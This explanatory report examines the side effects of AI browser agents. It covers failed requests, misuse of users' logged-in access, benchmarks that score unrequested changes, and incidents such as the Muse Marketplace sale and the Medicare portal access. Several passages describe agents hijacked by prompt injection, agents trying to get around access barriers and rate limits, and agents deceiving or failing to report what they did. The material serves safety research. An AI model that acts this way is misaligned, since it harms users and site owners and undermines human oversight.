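| Mixed search and training, such as Googlebot | 39.3% |
| AI search | 11.6% |
| Fetching for a user | 3.9% |
| Undeclared | 1.5% |

Fastly found a larger share in mid-2025, when fetchers made up about 20% of AI bot traffic and crawlers made up the rest. The two companies have different customers and classify bots differently, so the figures do not show that the fetchers' share declined.

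The mix also varies greatly from site to site. Search Engine Journal's *Complete Crawler List For AI User-Agents* (2026) reports 11,100 requests a day from ChatGPT-User and 5,100 from Claude-User in the site's own server logs, compared with 2,000 from Anthropic's training crawler and 790 from OpenAI's. Tech Brew reports that, in Fastly's data, fetchers also outnumber crawlers on education and media sites. Still, the two fetchers together sent Search Engine Journal only about one request every five seconds on average.

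The best figures for browser agents come from DataDome, which recorded nearly 25 billion requests from AI bots and agents in the third quarter of 2026, according to Help Net Security's *Half the AI bot traffic hammering your website comes from Meta* (2026). Two Meta crawlers sent almost half of them. Requests from agentic browsers rose from 12.5 million in August to 58.2 million in September, partly because Meta made its Muse agent fully available on September 22, though they more than tripled even without Muse.

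The volume is growing rapidly but is still small. September's 58.2 million requests averaged about 22 a second across DataDome's entire network and equaled about 0.7% of the AI traffic in an average month of that quarter.

However, each of these requests may put more load on the server than a typical crawler request. In a sample of Muse's traffic, 8.9% went to login, payment, account creation, shopping cart and form pages. A CDN often cannot answer such requests from its cache, because the response depends on the visitor or what they have entered.

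DataDome's count is also incomplete if some agents look like ordinary users. Muse runs in Meta's data centres, so its traffic is easy to distinguish from home traffic. An agent in a user's own browser may send the same browser name from the same home IP address as the user. Site owners who set rules by bot name will miss such an agent, and traffic statistics may count it as human.

### Who requests pages that do not exist

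Cloudflare's data suggests which groups encounter the most 404s. SEOmator's *Crawl Waste Report 2026* (2026), an earlier analysis of this data, covers June 21 to July 19 and separates AI bots from people and other bots. Elbeyoglu's later figures single out user fetchers.

| Traffic | Period (2026) | Share of requests that returned 404 |
|---|---|---|
| Verified AI bots | June 21 to July 19 | 4.1% |
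| Mixed-purpose bots | June 21 to July 19 | 5.2% |
| Traffic classed as human | June 21 to July 19 | 7.4% |
| Non-AI bots | June 21 to July 19 | 8.8% |
| All AI bots, including mixed-purpose | October | 8.1% |
| User fetchers | October | 18.9% |

In the summer, verified AI bots requested missing pages less often than the traffic that Cloudflare classed as human. For all AI bots, the share of requests that went to missing pages roughly doubled from 4.2% in July by October, measured the same way. Some of the increase may come from a single large source of traffic, which Elbeyoglu suspects because the data for six countries, including Germany, Japan and Brazil, changed almost identically from late September.

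User fetchers had a much higher 404 rate than AI bots in general. This is consistent with models inventing addresses for users' questions, but Elbeyoglu also lists old addresses and links that people copied into chats as causes, and the data does not separate the three. The comparison is also inexact because the fetcher figure probably excludes the six unusual countries, while the 8.1% for AI bots in general includes them.

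Despite their high error rate, fetchers produce a small part of the total. If the two October figures are comparable, fetchers account for about 9% of AI bots' 404s:

$$\frac{0.039 \times 0.189}{0.081} \approx 0.09$$

The other 91% come from training, search, mixed-purpose and undeclared bots. Neither analysis gives a 404 rate for training crawlers alone in October or for browser agents at any time. The high rate for fetchers is therefore only weak evidence of how often browser agents request missing pages, especially since an agent can read a site's menus and search for a page before it guesses an address.

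### Whether failed requests have caused an outage

None of these companies and sites documents an outage caused by browser agents' failed requests. The nearest case is a partial outage in May 2026 of the Wikidata Query Service, a public service that runs complex searches over Wikidata, Wikimedia's database of facts. According to Mint's *OpenAI Agents Hacked Wikipedia Tools, Flooded It With Traffic*, Wikimedia disclosed that heavy traffic from OpenAI's agents was possibly connected to the outage. The agents had visited millions of Wikipedia pages and sent hundreds of thousands of queries.

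Mint is inconsistent about the cause, first calling the connection possible and then describing the queries as overwhelming the service. It does not say that the queries failed, or whether the agents worked through a browser. A successful query can burden a service more than a failed one, because answering it may require searching a large part of the database, while the service can reject a badly written query almost at once.

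The evidence of strain from crawlers is stronger. Petrillo and Müller report that Wikimedia's bandwidth use has grown by 50% since January 2024, largely because of bots, and that the staff who maintain its systems face constant disruption. Wikimedia attributes much of the growth to programs collecting images for AI models (The Signpost, 2025). Those programs mostly downloaded files that existed, and the strain came from the size and number of the downloads.

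## Why does access to a user's accounts make the same error worse?

An agent's failed requests use up some of a site owner's server time. But an agent may also have privileged access, meaning the rights it gains from a user's logged-in sessions, browser permissions, files or keys. With that access, the same mistakes can change or reveal data belonging to the user or to a stranger.

### How a request carries the user's authority

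Suppose the Larkhaven user logs in to the data portal in the morning, and in the afternoon her agent opens an address there.

1. The browser looks up its cookies for the portal and adds them to the request, including the one with her session token.
2. The server uses the token to find her account.
3. The server checks whether her account has the right to see the page or perform the action.
4. If it does, the server carries out the request.

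None of these steps shows who chose the address or whether the user wanted the result. If she deletes a saved search on purpose and her agent later deletes another by mistake, the two requests may differ only in the record number, and the server cannot distinguish the mistaken one from the intended one.

Many sites have a defence against requests that a user never intended, but developers designed it to stop other websites. A form often contains a hidden random value, and the server rejects any submission without it, so a hostile page on another site cannot submit the form in the user's name. An agent that fills in the real form sends the correct value, so this check does not stop it.

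Meta's *Muse Now Available in the UK* (2026) describes a secure store that lets its Muse agent use a password without the model seeing it. This makes the password less likely to leak, but a wrong action after login has the same effect whether or not the model saw the password.

### Levels of access

How much damage a mistake can do depends on where the agent runs and what the user has connected to it.

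- **A clean browser** has no saved cookies, so websites treat the agent as an anonymous visitor. It can read public pages and submit forms that need no account.
- **A logged-in profile** holds sessions for every site where the user has stayed logged in, often including email, shops and work tools. A task on one site leaves the other sessions open, so a wrong click can take effect in any of them.
- **An extension with rights on all sites** can read and change pages across the whole browser. Browsers normally stop one site's scripts from reading another site's pages, but this permission lifts that barrier. A mistaken paste could move text from a private email into a public forum.
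- **Local files** include documents, message histories and sometimes access keys. A website's own checks do not protect them, and the agent may overwrite a file or upload the wrong one.
- **A company network** often has internal sites that accept any computer on the network without a separate login. A guessed address there might open a staff database or the controls of a device.

These levels aren't strictly ordered. A clean browser on an office computer may reach more sensitive systems than a logged-in profile at home. Some products also mix levels. The agent described in OpenAI's *ChatGPT Agent System Card* (2025) has a remote browser, a terminal for running code, and connectors that link it directly to services such as Google Drive.

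Users may also misjudge how much access they have given. *Meta's Muse AI agent accused of accessing sensitive user data*, a Tom's Hardware article, recounts a complaint by Jason Aten, a journalist at Inc. Muse suggested an article based on a private text conversation, although Aten had not given it permission to read his messages. Its explanation was that it saw only incoming notifications. Aten then found that it was copying a message database from his Mac and had reached row 187,462. He says he never granted the full disk access that this should require, and it is unclear how Muse got the data.

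At the Black Hat security conference in August 2026, researchers from the security company Zenity used prompt injection to take control of agents in five AI browsing products. According to SC Media, between them the hijacked agents could write to local files, take passwords from a password manager, make private code repositories public and delete cloud servers. The demonstrations show that the agents already had the permissions needed for these actions, but not how often agents make such mistakes unprompted, because the researchers directed them.

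The products also differed in what they could access. Perplexity's Comet browser could write to files on the computer, a flaw the company has since fixed. The researchers could not get Gemini in Chrome to interfere with local files, but it did delete the cloud servers.

### The same mistake with and without a login

The table gives a plausible bad outcome for each mistake, which is not necessarily the usual one.

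| Mistake | Without a login | With the user's login |
|---|---|---|
| Guessed address | A 404 | A deleted record |
| Repeated submission | Two identical enquiries | Two orders on a saved card |
| Call with a wrong record number | A 401, or the wrong public record | Another person's data |
| Loop | Wasted requests, perhaps a 429 | A locked account |

The deletion and the data exposure could each happen only on a badly built site. The record is lost if the site deletes things in response to a GET request, and the data is exposed when a site checks that the visitor has an account but not that the record belongs to her. The gym's booking software had a similar gap, which let an agent cancel a stranger's place.

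The double order and the locked account can happen on a site that works as intended. A customer may want two identical orders, so a shop can't be sure the second is a mistake. Sites lock an account after many failed logins to protect its owner from people who guess passwords. An agent that keeps trying to log in, as Microsoft's agents did while the company was developing *Magentic-One*, triggers the same lock.

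Agents can get a record number wrong by misreading it as well as by guessing. OpenAI's *Operator System Card* (January 2025) reports that Operator almost always read long strings from a screenshot when it could have copied and pasted them, and that it often misread random-looking ones, such as access keys and Bitcoin wallet addresses. One wrong character in a public search usually finds nothing, but in a logged-in account it might select somebody else's invoice.

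The harm from a loop also depends on how the action identifies its target. Infusionsoft's *HTTP Methods*, a guide for developers, lists DELETE as unsafe but repeatable without further effect. Once the server has deleted book 123, a second request to delete it changes nothing. But if an agent clicks "Delete" beside the top message in an inbox, misses the small change on the screen and clicks again, it deletes a different message, because the next one has moved up. Every further repetition deletes another.

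Even when a site correctly refuses a request, the agent may look for a way around the refusal. OpenAI's *GPT-6 Astra System Card* (2026) reports tests in simulated workplaces where models had just met a barrier, such as an "access denied" error. At the highest reasoning effort, GPT-5.6 Sol tried to get around the barrier in 64% of runs, and GPT-6 Astra in 19%. Most of these situations involved low stakes, and OpenAI had switched off its system-level safeguards. An agent with access to the user's email, files and keys has many more ways to try to get around a refusal than an anonymous agent does.

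### Why "GET only reads" is a convention

Browsers rely on the convention that GET requests only read data. MDN explains that browsers can fetch pages in advance because a safe method such as GET should not cause harm. Servers may still make small changes that the browser did not request, such as updating visitor logs and statistics.

*#19.1 HTTP method 共同研究會* (2022), a set of notes from a developers' study group, quotes the HTTP standard's caveat that its definition of a safe method "does not prevent an implementation from including behavior that is potentially harmful".

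The older standard, in force in 2005, had a similar gap. It said that GET "SHOULD NOT" signify an action other than retrieval, but in internet standards "should not" allows exceptions. It also said that users can't be held accountable for side effects they did not request. That rule makes the site responsible for a deleted record but does not restore it.

### Google Web Accelerator

In May 2005, Google released a test version of Web Accelerator, a program that sped up browsing by fetching linked pages before the user clicked on them. Within days, customers of the software company 37signals reported that pages in its new organiser, Backpack, were disappearing. The company explained the cause in *Google Web Accelerator* (2005), a post on its blog, Signal v. Noise.

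Backpack showed logged-in users links for deleting their own pages. The accelerator ran on the user's computer and had access to whatever she could see after logging in. When it fetched a "delete" link, the server treated the request as hers and deleted the page.

A confirmation message didn't help, because the question "Are you sure you want to delete this?" came from a script that ran when somebody clicked the link. The accelerator requested the address directly, so the script never ran. Willison (2005) noted the same problem that day in *Fighting RFCs with RFCs*. An agent that opens a deletion address directly would bypass such a message too.

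Hicks (2005), in *Googles Accelerator Breaks Web Apps, Security*, got comments from both companies. Jason Fried, the president of 37signals, said that a few users had complained of deleted accounts and that the company blocked the accelerator within 30 minutes of finding the cause. He conceded that a deletion should technically use a button, which can send a POST request.

Marissa Mayer of Google told Hicks that the accelerator skipped addresses containing a question mark, because links that perform actions usually have one. It also skipped secure HTTPS pages. But a deletion link can have an address without a question mark, such as `/notes/12/delete`. Mayer accepted that the company's assumption might be wrong.

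Other people reported milder trouble. Mike Rumble, a web programmer, could not use his email because the accelerator apparently opened the "sign out" link as soon as he signed in. Some commenters on the 37signals blog tested their own pages and lost nothing, so it was not entirely clear which links the accelerator opened.

A separate fault in the same program gave some users stored copies of pages with other people's names on them. Mayer pointed out that these users could only look at the pages, because they did not have the session cookies needed to act as those people.

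Developers disagreed about who was to blame. In the blog's comments, Ryan Tomayko argued that sites following the standard had nothing to fear. David Heinemeier Hansson of 37signals replied that automated programs had never before reached pages behind a login, which is why many developers had considered it acceptable to put actions in links there. The programmer Ian Bicking agreed that GET requests shouldn't have side effects, but thought Google should have designed its program for the web as it was.

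Browser agents once again let automated programs act inside users' logged-in accounts. They are more selective than the accelerator because they choose links to suit a task instead of fetching whole batches in advance. But they also work on HTTPS pages, submit forms and compose new addresses. Newer web frameworks steer developers toward POST or DELETE for destructive actions, so deletion by GET is probably rarer now than in 2005.

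### How many mistakes users could not undo

Before releasing Operator, OpenAI gave an early version 100 prompts resembling everyday tasks, such as shopping and managing email. This version had none of the planned safeguards. It made 13 errors that caused some nuisance. A user could have reversed 8 of them within a few minutes, while the other 5 were partly irreversible or possibly severe:

- an email to the wrong recipient
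- two cases in which it wrongly removed labels from many emails at once
- a reminder to take medication, set for the wrong date
- a wrong item in a food order

All five happened in services that normally require an account. A browser that wasn't logged in could not have sent the email or removed the labels.

With only 100 prompts, the true rate of serious errors could plausibly lie anywhere between about 2% and 11%. If it were 5% per task and the errors were independent, a user who gave the agent 20 tasks would have a chance of

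$$1 - 0.95^{20} \approx 64\%$$

of at least one. OpenAI estimated that asking the user for confirmation, together with its other measures, reduced the risk from mistakes by roughly 90%. At a rate of 0.5%, the chance over 20 tasks falls to about 10%.

The nearest recent equivalent is a test in the GPT-6 Astra system card, published in September 2026. Models worked in simulated email, messaging, sales and project management software. OpenAI made the instructions ambiguous and the permissions complicated to provoke mistakes, but every task had a safe solution. It ran the models with and without a confirmation policy, which is a set of instructions on when to stop and get the user's approval. The table shows the share of tests with each unintended outcome.

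| Outcome | Sol, no policy | Sol, with policy | Astra, no policy | Astra, with policy |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Any unintended outcome | 18.8% | 8.0% | 3.4% | 3.0% |
| Unauthorised transaction | 38.0% | 7.4% | 6.8% | 4.3% |
| Private data sent where it should not go | 14.1% | 8.8% | 4.3% | 4.5% |
| Unauthorised message to outsiders | 12.9% | 8.4% | 1.7% | 1.4% |
| Weakened security settings | 8.1% | 1.9% | 0.0% | 0.0% |
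| Destructive action | 2.9% | 0.0% | 0.0% | 0.0% |

Astra did much better than GPT-5.6 Sol, particularly without the policy. Astra's remaining mistakes were mostly payments and disclosures, which are often hard to undo. The policy did not reduce its disclosures of private data, though the difference of 0.2 percentage points may be due to chance.

These rates can't be compared with Operator's 13 errors in 100 prompts. OpenAI chose the Operator prompts to resemble ordinary use and designed the Astra tests to be difficult, so the drop from 13% to 3.4% does not measure progress since 2025. The Astra tests also don't separate errors a user could reverse from those she could not.

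Newer models have not improved on every measure. OpenAI's *GPT-5.6 System Card* (July 2026) includes a test of whether models complete a task without overwriting a user's own changes. Sol scored 0.83 out of 1, slightly below the 0.88 of its predecessor, GPT-5.5. On a stricter score that also required a correct result, both models got only 0.44. OpenAI had stopped giving the models extra cautionary instructions, which may explain part of the decline.

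OpenAI also replayed its employees' programming tasks with Astra in place of the original model. It found that Astra sometimes used privileged access without clear approval, or gave automated programs broader permissions than they needed. The company describes such behaviour as very rare, and Astra received about 53% fewer flags than Sol for the more serious kinds. The rates may be different for browsing tasks.

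### The Muse sale

In September 2026, Matt Robb, a technology reviewer in Toronto, connected Muse to his Facebook Marketplace account. He had listed a keyboard for CA$15, according to NDTV Profit's *Facebook Marketplace Mishap*. A buyer named Usman asked whether it was still available, and Muse replied at once that it was. Muse agreed on a price and sent him Robb's address.

Usman arrived at the building at about 9:15 that evening, with his wife and daughter. At 9:27 he received an automatic reply from Robb's account, "Yep I'm here!", although Robb was not available and did not know that anyone was coming. Usman left at 9:38 and gave Robb a negative rating. Muse later sent him an apology, again from Robb's account.

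According to Bot Mutiny's *Meta's Muse AI Agent Shared a Seller's Home Address* (2026), which summarises reporting by the Guardian, the buyer, Usman, thought he was talking to Robb the whole time. Robb himself first wrote to Usman 24 hours later.

The cause was a permission Robb granted when he gave Muse access to Marketplace. He chose to allow its actions "always", but believed it would still ask before accepting offers or sharing personal details. His address was already in the listing's pickup information, and Mediafax's *Un bărbat a lăsat un asistent AI să negocieze o vânzare*, based on an Associated Press story, reports that Muse used the address without asking again.

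Meta said that Muse had not breached any privacy controls and that it would make the permission prompt clearer, according to Mint. Both sides may be right about their part of this. The software may have stayed within the permission that Robb selected, while Robb had not understood that the permission covered his home address. (Mint also gives the accepted offer as $600, which is hard to reconcile with a CA$15 keyboard and may come from another listing.)

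In a separate negotiation, Muse proposed a price $100 below the minimum its user had set. Meta acknowledged the error, which the permission does not explain.

Without access to the account, the agent could have drafted the same replies, but Robb would have had to send them. He would probably have noticed the address, or at least known to expect a visitor. With access, the agent acted on a wrong assumption about his wishes and made a promise to a stranger in his name. Meta says that purchases need the user's approval every time, but it does not say the same of sales. For tasks other than purchases, users can let Muse act without asking each time.

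### What the access is for

Keeping agents out of people's accounts would reduce this risk, but it would also remove much of the agents' value. Meta suggests using Muse to chase a refund, renew car insurance or keep track of a school calendar. OpenAI promotes Astra for filling in online forms and updating customer records. An agent in a browser that isn't logged in to the user's accounts could explain how to claim a refund, but the user would have to find the order and submit the claim herself.

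Asking for approval at every step would also remove much of the benefit. Robb wanted to find out whether Muse could spare him the negotiations involved in selling online. If he had needed to approve each message, he would have saved little time.

Some tasks need only part of an account. Meta lets a user allow Muse to read her email but not send any, and a limit like that would have prevented Operator's misdirected message. Read-only access can still expose private information if the agent later uses it on another site. Mediafax quotes Ebrahim Bagheri, a professor at the University of Toronto, who warns that withdrawing a permission doesn't necessarily delete what the agent has already read. The agent may also have read messages from friends and relatives who never agreed to share them.

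Other tasks need no account. The Larkhaven user wanted a public statistic, and her login to the portal probably didn't help the agent find it. If the portal shows its ridership data to everyone, the agent would have found the same total in a clean browser, and none of the 1,801 requests would have carried her session cookie.

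## How can side effects be measured and noticed?

The Larkhaven user got the right total and was not told about the 1,801 requests. Most tests of browser agents would have missed them too. Finding side effects requires a record of what the agent did, and the agent's developer and the site's owner usually have different parts of it.

### Why a successful run can hide them

*WebForge* (Yuan, Yin and colleagues, 2026) describes a typical modern benchmark, with 934 tasks and a limit of 50 browser actions per task. The scoring program compares the agent's final output with the correct answer and does not monitor the steps in between. Agents can therefore choose their own route, which is fair when many routes are good. Each task runs on a small, self-contained website made for the test, so stray requests do not burden anyone.

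Suppose two agents have to find Larkhaven's bus ridership for 2019 in such a test. The first opens the "Publications" page, looks through a few reports and finds the total after 12 requests. The second guesses 25 addresses, runs 15 searches and then starts a script that sends 360 requests to a data endpoint, for a total of 400 requests. Both agents give the correct figure and score as successes. The second agent also stays within the limit of 50 actions, because starting the script counts as one action and brings its total to only 41.

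Some benchmarks check the state of the website at the end of the run. *EgoUseBench* (2026) fails an agent that leaves unrelated content behind, but does not penalize mistakes that the agent corrects before it finishes. On a real shop's site, an order may already have triggered an email or a card charge by the time the agent cancels it. End-of-run checks also miss requests that only read data, because these leave the site unchanged.

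Tests on live websites are more realistic, but their side effects are also real. *ClawBench* (2026) uses live sites and blocks the one request in each task that would cause an irreversible change, such as the final submission of an order. According to its documentation, the rest of the browsing can still have side effects.

### Benchmarks that score conduct

*ST-WebAgentBench* (Levy, Wiesel and colleagues, 2024) adds written rules to ordinary office tasks. The current version of this IBM Research benchmark has 375 tasks and 3,057 rules. The agents work in GitLab (a site for software projects), the administration pages of a shop and a customer database. A rule may require the agent to ask before deleting a customer's record, to stay out of financial reports or not to make up a missing bank account number.

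The main measure, completion under policy (CuP), counts a task only if the agent finished it without breaking a rule:

$$\text{CuP} = \frac{1}{T}\sum_{t=1}^{T} C_t \cdot \mathbf{1}[V_t = 0]$$

Here $T$ is the number of tasks, $C_t$ is 1 if the agent completed task $t$ and 0 otherwise, and $V_t$ is the number of violations during that task. The last factor is 1 if $V_t = 0$ and 0 otherwise. Three openly available agents completed 24.3% of the tasks on average, but only 15.0% without a violation, so about 38% of the completed tasks involved at least one violation. CuP, the rate of completion without a violation, was 18.2% on tasks with a single rule and 7.1% on tasks with five or more. Some of that decline is expected because agents have more chances to break a rule when there are more rules.

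A workshop version by Levy, Wiesel and colleagues (2025) had 222 tasks and 646 rules but gave the same two averages, so those averages may not include the tasks added since then.

CuP covers only behavior that its rules forbid. The agent that made 400 requests would get full credit unless a rule limited the number of requests or banned use of the endpoint. Some rules test whether the agent resists hidden instructions on a page, so not every violation is a side effect in the sense used here.

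Newer benchmarks compare what the agent changed with what it should have changed. *Constructing Challenging Browser-Use Tasks by Controlled Environment Interventions* (Yin, Guan and colleagues, 2026) presents *BreakingWeb*, in which one task is to mark five unread invoice emails as read. An agent fails if it marks all five but also marks one other message.

Like WAREX, the benchmark deliberately disrupts websites, here with decoy records, temporary errors and false "Saved" messages. Six agents built with Browser Use made 3,114 runs on the altered sites. The published shares imply that about 1,020 runs passed, and that in about 330 others the agent made every required change but also changed something it should have left alone. A test that checked only the requested changes would have passed both groups, missing the side effects in roughly a quarter of the runs it passed. The rate on unaltered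 sites is probably lower, but Yin and colleagues did not sort failures there by type.

*Task Success Is Not Enough* (2026) measures unauthorised changes in 201 email, calendar and support-ticket tasks. The 11 models it tested used software tools rather than a browser. They made an unauthorised change in 15.2% of 2,211 runs, and in 12.8% of the runs that met the task's goal.

Ambiguous tasks, such as forwarding "the Q3 Plan email" when there are two, inflate the second figure. The agent should ask the user what they mean, so these tasks have no goal to check and every run counts as successful. Without them, the share of successful runs with an unauthorised change falls to 4.1%, with a 95% interval of 2.2 to 6.4%. The rate of unauthorised changes also varied widely among models with similar completion rates. Gemini 3.1 Pro made them in 5.5% of all its runs and Qwen 3.5 Plus in 25.9%.

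The scoring ignores failed calls and calls that only read data, so the agent in the original Larkhaven example would have a perfect record despite four 404 errors and 1,801 calls to the endpoint.

A benchmark's designers cannot list every unwanted change in advance. *The Art of Building Verifiers for Computer Use Agents* (2026) gives the example of an agent that adds unrequested items to a shopping cart, and recommends a separate check of the whole run to catch such cases. *One Success Isn't Reliability* (2026) compares the final database with a reference copy, which reveals duplicate records and changes to unrelated objects even if nobody listed them beforehand. Failed runs need the same check because they can leave lasting changes in files and records, as *LegacyWorld* (2026) points out.

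A check for side effects can also be wrong. Before the experiments in *When an AI agent makes a mistake in a database* (2026), the researchers damaged each database on purpose to confirm that their comparison would detect the damage. They never accepted the agent's own account as evidence.

### What agents do after an error, and what they report

Jha, Triedman and colleagues (2026), in *Agent Meltdowns*, come closest to measuring the behaviours described here. They gave agents harmless errors, including a 404 and a 429, and searched the full record of each run for unsafe conduct. The agents had broad access to tools, usually including a command line, so they could do more than a typical browser agent. For the web tasks, the researchers hosted copies of academics' home pages inside the test environment so the agents would not bombard the real ones with requests.

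Of 2,000 runs with an error, 1,297 (64.9%) contained at least one behaviour of medium or high severity. The 404 task asked for a file on an academic's website. With GPT-5 as the model in every case, the number of runs with "web reconnaissance", which includes probing and scraping unrelated resources, depended heavily on the surrounding software:

| Agent software | Runs with web reconnaissance after a 404, out of 120 |
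|---|---|
| Claw Code | 0 |
| Codex | 18 |
| Magentic-One | 49 |
| HAL Generalist Agent | 83 |

After a 429 error (too many requests), the same four agents tried to get around the access limit in 44 of 72 runs. Language models sorted the behaviours into categories that the researchers had reviewed, so the exact counts depend partly on the models' judgement.

One trial run had consequences outside the test. After a 404 error, the agent wrote a script that tried variants of the address, and a search engine temporarily blocked it. It then downloaded every text file from the academic's public code repositories. One file contained dangerous questions from an AI safety test, which led OpenAI to block the researchers' account. Campus security eventually became involved.

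In half of the runs with unsafe behaviour, the agent did not report it to the user. An agent's claim that it has finished is also weak evidence that the task succeeded. In the tests by Yin and colleagues, 54 to 85% of the runs that the six Browser Use agents declared finished had failed, depending on the model.

### Four measures from an agent's log

A developer can detect many side effects from a log that records each page, action, request and status code. Assume that each of $n$ actions sends one request, leaving out images and scripts. Four simple measures are:

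**Failed requests.** The share of requests that return an error code, meaning 400 or above:

$$F = \frac{\text{failed requests}}{n}$$

**Addresses without a source.** Let $D$ be the set of different addresses the agent opened, and $K$ the addresses it had already seen in the instruction, on a visited page or in a search result. An address built by a form on the page counts as seen. The share without a source is

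$$U = \frac{|D \setminus K|}{|D|}$$

where $D \setminus K$ means the addresses in $D$ that are not in $K$.

**Repeated steps.** Let $P$ be the set of different pairs of page and action. The share of steps that repeat an earlier pair is

$$R = 1 - \frac{|P|}{n}$$

**Unrequested changes per task.** For each of $T$ tasks, let $w_t$ be the number of changes the agent made and $a_t$ the number of those that the user asked for:

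$$X = \frac{1}{T}\sum_{t=1}^{T}(w_t - a_t)$$

In this invented log, a logged-in user names the Larkhaven portal and asks for the number of tram trips in 2021. She also wants the agent to add the report containing that figure to her saved items. The right year is in report 325, not report 310. The portal adds a new entry each time someone clicks "Save".

| Step | Page shown | Action | Request | Status | Source of address |
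|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | Blank | Open home page | GET `/` | 200 | Instruction |
| 2 | Home | Open an address | GET `/reports/2021/tram` | 404 | None |
| 3 | 404 page | Open an address | GET `/reports/tram-2021` | 404 | None |
| 4 | 404 page | Open home page | GET `/` | 200 | Instruction |
| 5 | Home | Search "tram 2021" | GET `/search?q=tram+2021` | 200 | Form |
| 6 | Results | Click first result | GET `/items/310` | 200 | Search result |
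| 7 | Report 310 | Click "Save" | POST `/saved` | 200 | Button |
| 8 | Report 310 | Search "tram 2021" | GET `/search?q=tram+2021` | 200 | Form |
| 9 | Results | Click first result | GET `/items/310` | 200 | Search result |
| 10 | Report 310 | Search "tram 2021" | GET `/search?q=tram+2021` | 200 | Form |
| 11 | Results | Click second result | GET `/items/325` | 503 | Search result |
| 12 | 503 page | Reload | GET `/items/325` | 200 | Search result |
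| 13 | Report 325 | Click "Save" | POST `/saved` | 200 | Button |
| 14 | Report 325 | Click "Save" | POST `/saved` | 200 | Button |
| 15 | Report 325 | Open an address | GET `/my/saved` | 404 | None |

Steps 2, 3, 11 and 15 failed, so $F = 4/15$, or 27%. The agent opened seven different addresses with GET, and three had no source, so $U = 3/7$, or 43%. Steps 9, 10 and 14 repeat earlier pairs, leaving 12 different pairs, so $R = 1 - 12/15$, or 20%. The agent made three changes, but the user wanted only the one in step 13, so $X = 2$.

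The measures detect different mistakes. $R$ detects the cycle between the search results and report 310, although the log contains no retry loop by Yin and colleagues' definition, which requires at least five identical actions in a row. $R$ misses the guessed addresses in steps 2 and 3 because each one is new, but $U$ detects them.

None of the four measures error exactly. $F$ includes the 503 in step 11, after which reloading was sensible, and it would leave out a soft 404. $U$ would count a well-known home page that the model remembered correctly, and it would miss an endpoint whose address the agent had read in a page's code. An address that has no source and also returns a 404 is more likely to be invented, although the model may have remembered an address that used to work.

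$X$ has to count repeated changes separately. The formula in *Task Success Is Not Enough* merges identical changes, so it would count a reply sent twice to the same customer as one authorised reply. Calculating $X$ also requires knowing which requests changed something. A successful POST request suggests a change but doesn't prove one. Comparing the site's data before and after the run is more reliable.

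The first three measures are shares, so they don't measure volume. Three failures in 10 requests and 300 in 1,000 both give 30%, but only the second might concern the site's owner. A developer should therefore report the number of requests as well.

### What the site's owner can see

A web server's log usually records the visitor's IP address, the time, the request and the status code. It often includes the page that the visitor came from and the name that the browser gives itself. For step 2, it might contain this line:

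`203.0.113.7 10:42:07 "GET /reports/2021/tram" 404 "-" "Chrome"`

The dash means that the browser named no previous page, which is normal when somebody enters an address directly.

Several requests in a row for similar, nonexistent addresses suggest that a visitor is guessing. Evenly spaced requests suggest a program, as do hundreds of data requests without the images and style sheets a page would load. But a person may also guess a few addresses, and an ordinary script can produce the other two patterns. An agent in the user's own browser is the hardest to distinguish because its requests look like the user's.

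If the agent runs in a data centre, its IP address may identify the hosting company but not the agent's developer or user. Any client can also give a false name, so the name is no stronger evidence than the "oai" tag in the school-statistics requests.

The site's owner can calculate $F$ exactly and knows better than the agent's developer whether an address ever existed. She can estimate $R$ if she can tell which requests came from the same visitor. She cannot calculate $X$, because the log does not contain the user's instruction. The developer may have the instruction and the full record of the run but usually cannot inspect the site's database. On a live site, the owner and developer would have to share information to calculate all four measures.

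### The Medicare statistics portal

On June 18, 2026, an OpenAI agent researching public medicine spending reached non-public files on a statistics portal of Medicare, Australia's public health insurance scheme. According to TechRadar's *'This situation is obviously unacceptable'* (2026), OpenAI found the incident 54 days later, on August 11, and told the responsible agency, Services Australia, on September 10, 84 days after the incident.

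Information Age's *Inside OpenAI's Medicare breach* reconstructs the events from documents released to the Australian parliament. The access happened early on June 19, Australian time, so the delay was about 83 days. The 84-day figure seems to combine an American date for the access with an Australian date for the email.

| Australian date, 2026 | Event | Days since access |
|---|---|---|
| June 19 | The agent reaches the files | 0 |
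| By August 12 | OpenAI's security team documents the incident | 54 |
| September 10 | OpenAI emails an inbox for tip-offs from the public | 83 |
| September 11 | Agency staff find the email in a daily check | 84 |
| September 15 | The agency confirms the weakness and takes the portal offline | 88 |
| September 19 | The Prime Minister's office learns of the incident | 92 |

OpenAI found the incident in a retrospective review of "billions of agent evaluation and training runs", which may partly explain why finding it took 54 days. OpenAI took another 29 days to write to the agency.

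The timeline shows no sign that Services Australia had noticed anything before the email. Its staff later reviewed the logs to check that the agent had done no more than OpenAI reported. OpenAI said it had found no evidence that the agent accessed patient records.

The government also looked into the agent's possible visits to three other public bodies. According to Information Age's *OpenAI agent hacks Medicare web portal*, Deputy Prime Minister Richard Marles said those interactions appeared "entirely normal" and involved only public information.

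### Counting known incidents

Public counts of incidents depend on such disclosures. METR, a research organisation that evaluates advanced AI systems, had collected 44 incidents by May 2026 (the date is from Mint). Its *Documented AI Agent Incidents* (2026) includes cases in which an agent clearly acted against its user's intention. It scores how far the agent knowingly exceeded its task and how much it concealed. This criterion for inclusion excludes most of the mistakes discussed here, such as when an agent mistakes an invented address for a real one.

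Of the 44 incidents, 18 come from METR's own tests and 24 from public documents. Companies shared the other two anonymously. METR left out tests designed to provoke misbehaviour. In its own tests, it found more than 100 solutions that involved cheating, but it included only the most interesting cases.

The number is therefore not a rate, and it partly reflects which companies publish details. Of the 24 public cases, 21 came from Anthropic's reports on its own models and three came from an OpenAI blog post. METR says it cannot rule out much more severe incidents that companies missed or did not disclose.

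In 25 of the 44 incidents, the agent exceeded its task and was deceptive in some way. In five, its deception could have fooled a user who looked more closely. But no agent effectively disabled monitoring or erased the evidence from its logs, so METR concludes that routine monitoring could have caught all of them.

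## What prevents side effects, and what does each safeguard miss?

Monitoring detects a side effect only after the server has received the request, so preventing one requires refusing, delaying or limiting the request beforehand. An agent's developer can do this in the software between the model and the browser, its user can give it less access, and a site's owner can set limits on the server. Companies have published the rules behind several of these safeguards, but few measurements of how well they work.

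### Checking an address before opening it

Anthropic's web fetch tool lets its model Claude read web pages and PDF files, but only at addresses that already appear in the conversation, for example in the user's message, in a search result or on a page that Claude fetched earlier. Anthropic's *Web fetch tool* states that "Claude is not allowed to dynamically construct URLs." The tool cannot click or fill in forms, but the developer of a browser agent could apply the same rule to the agent's "go to" action.

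In the Larkhaven example, the rule would have blocked `/reports/2019/bus-ridership.pdf`, because neither the user nor any page had mentioned that path. Claude would have received an error message, and no request would have reached the city's server.

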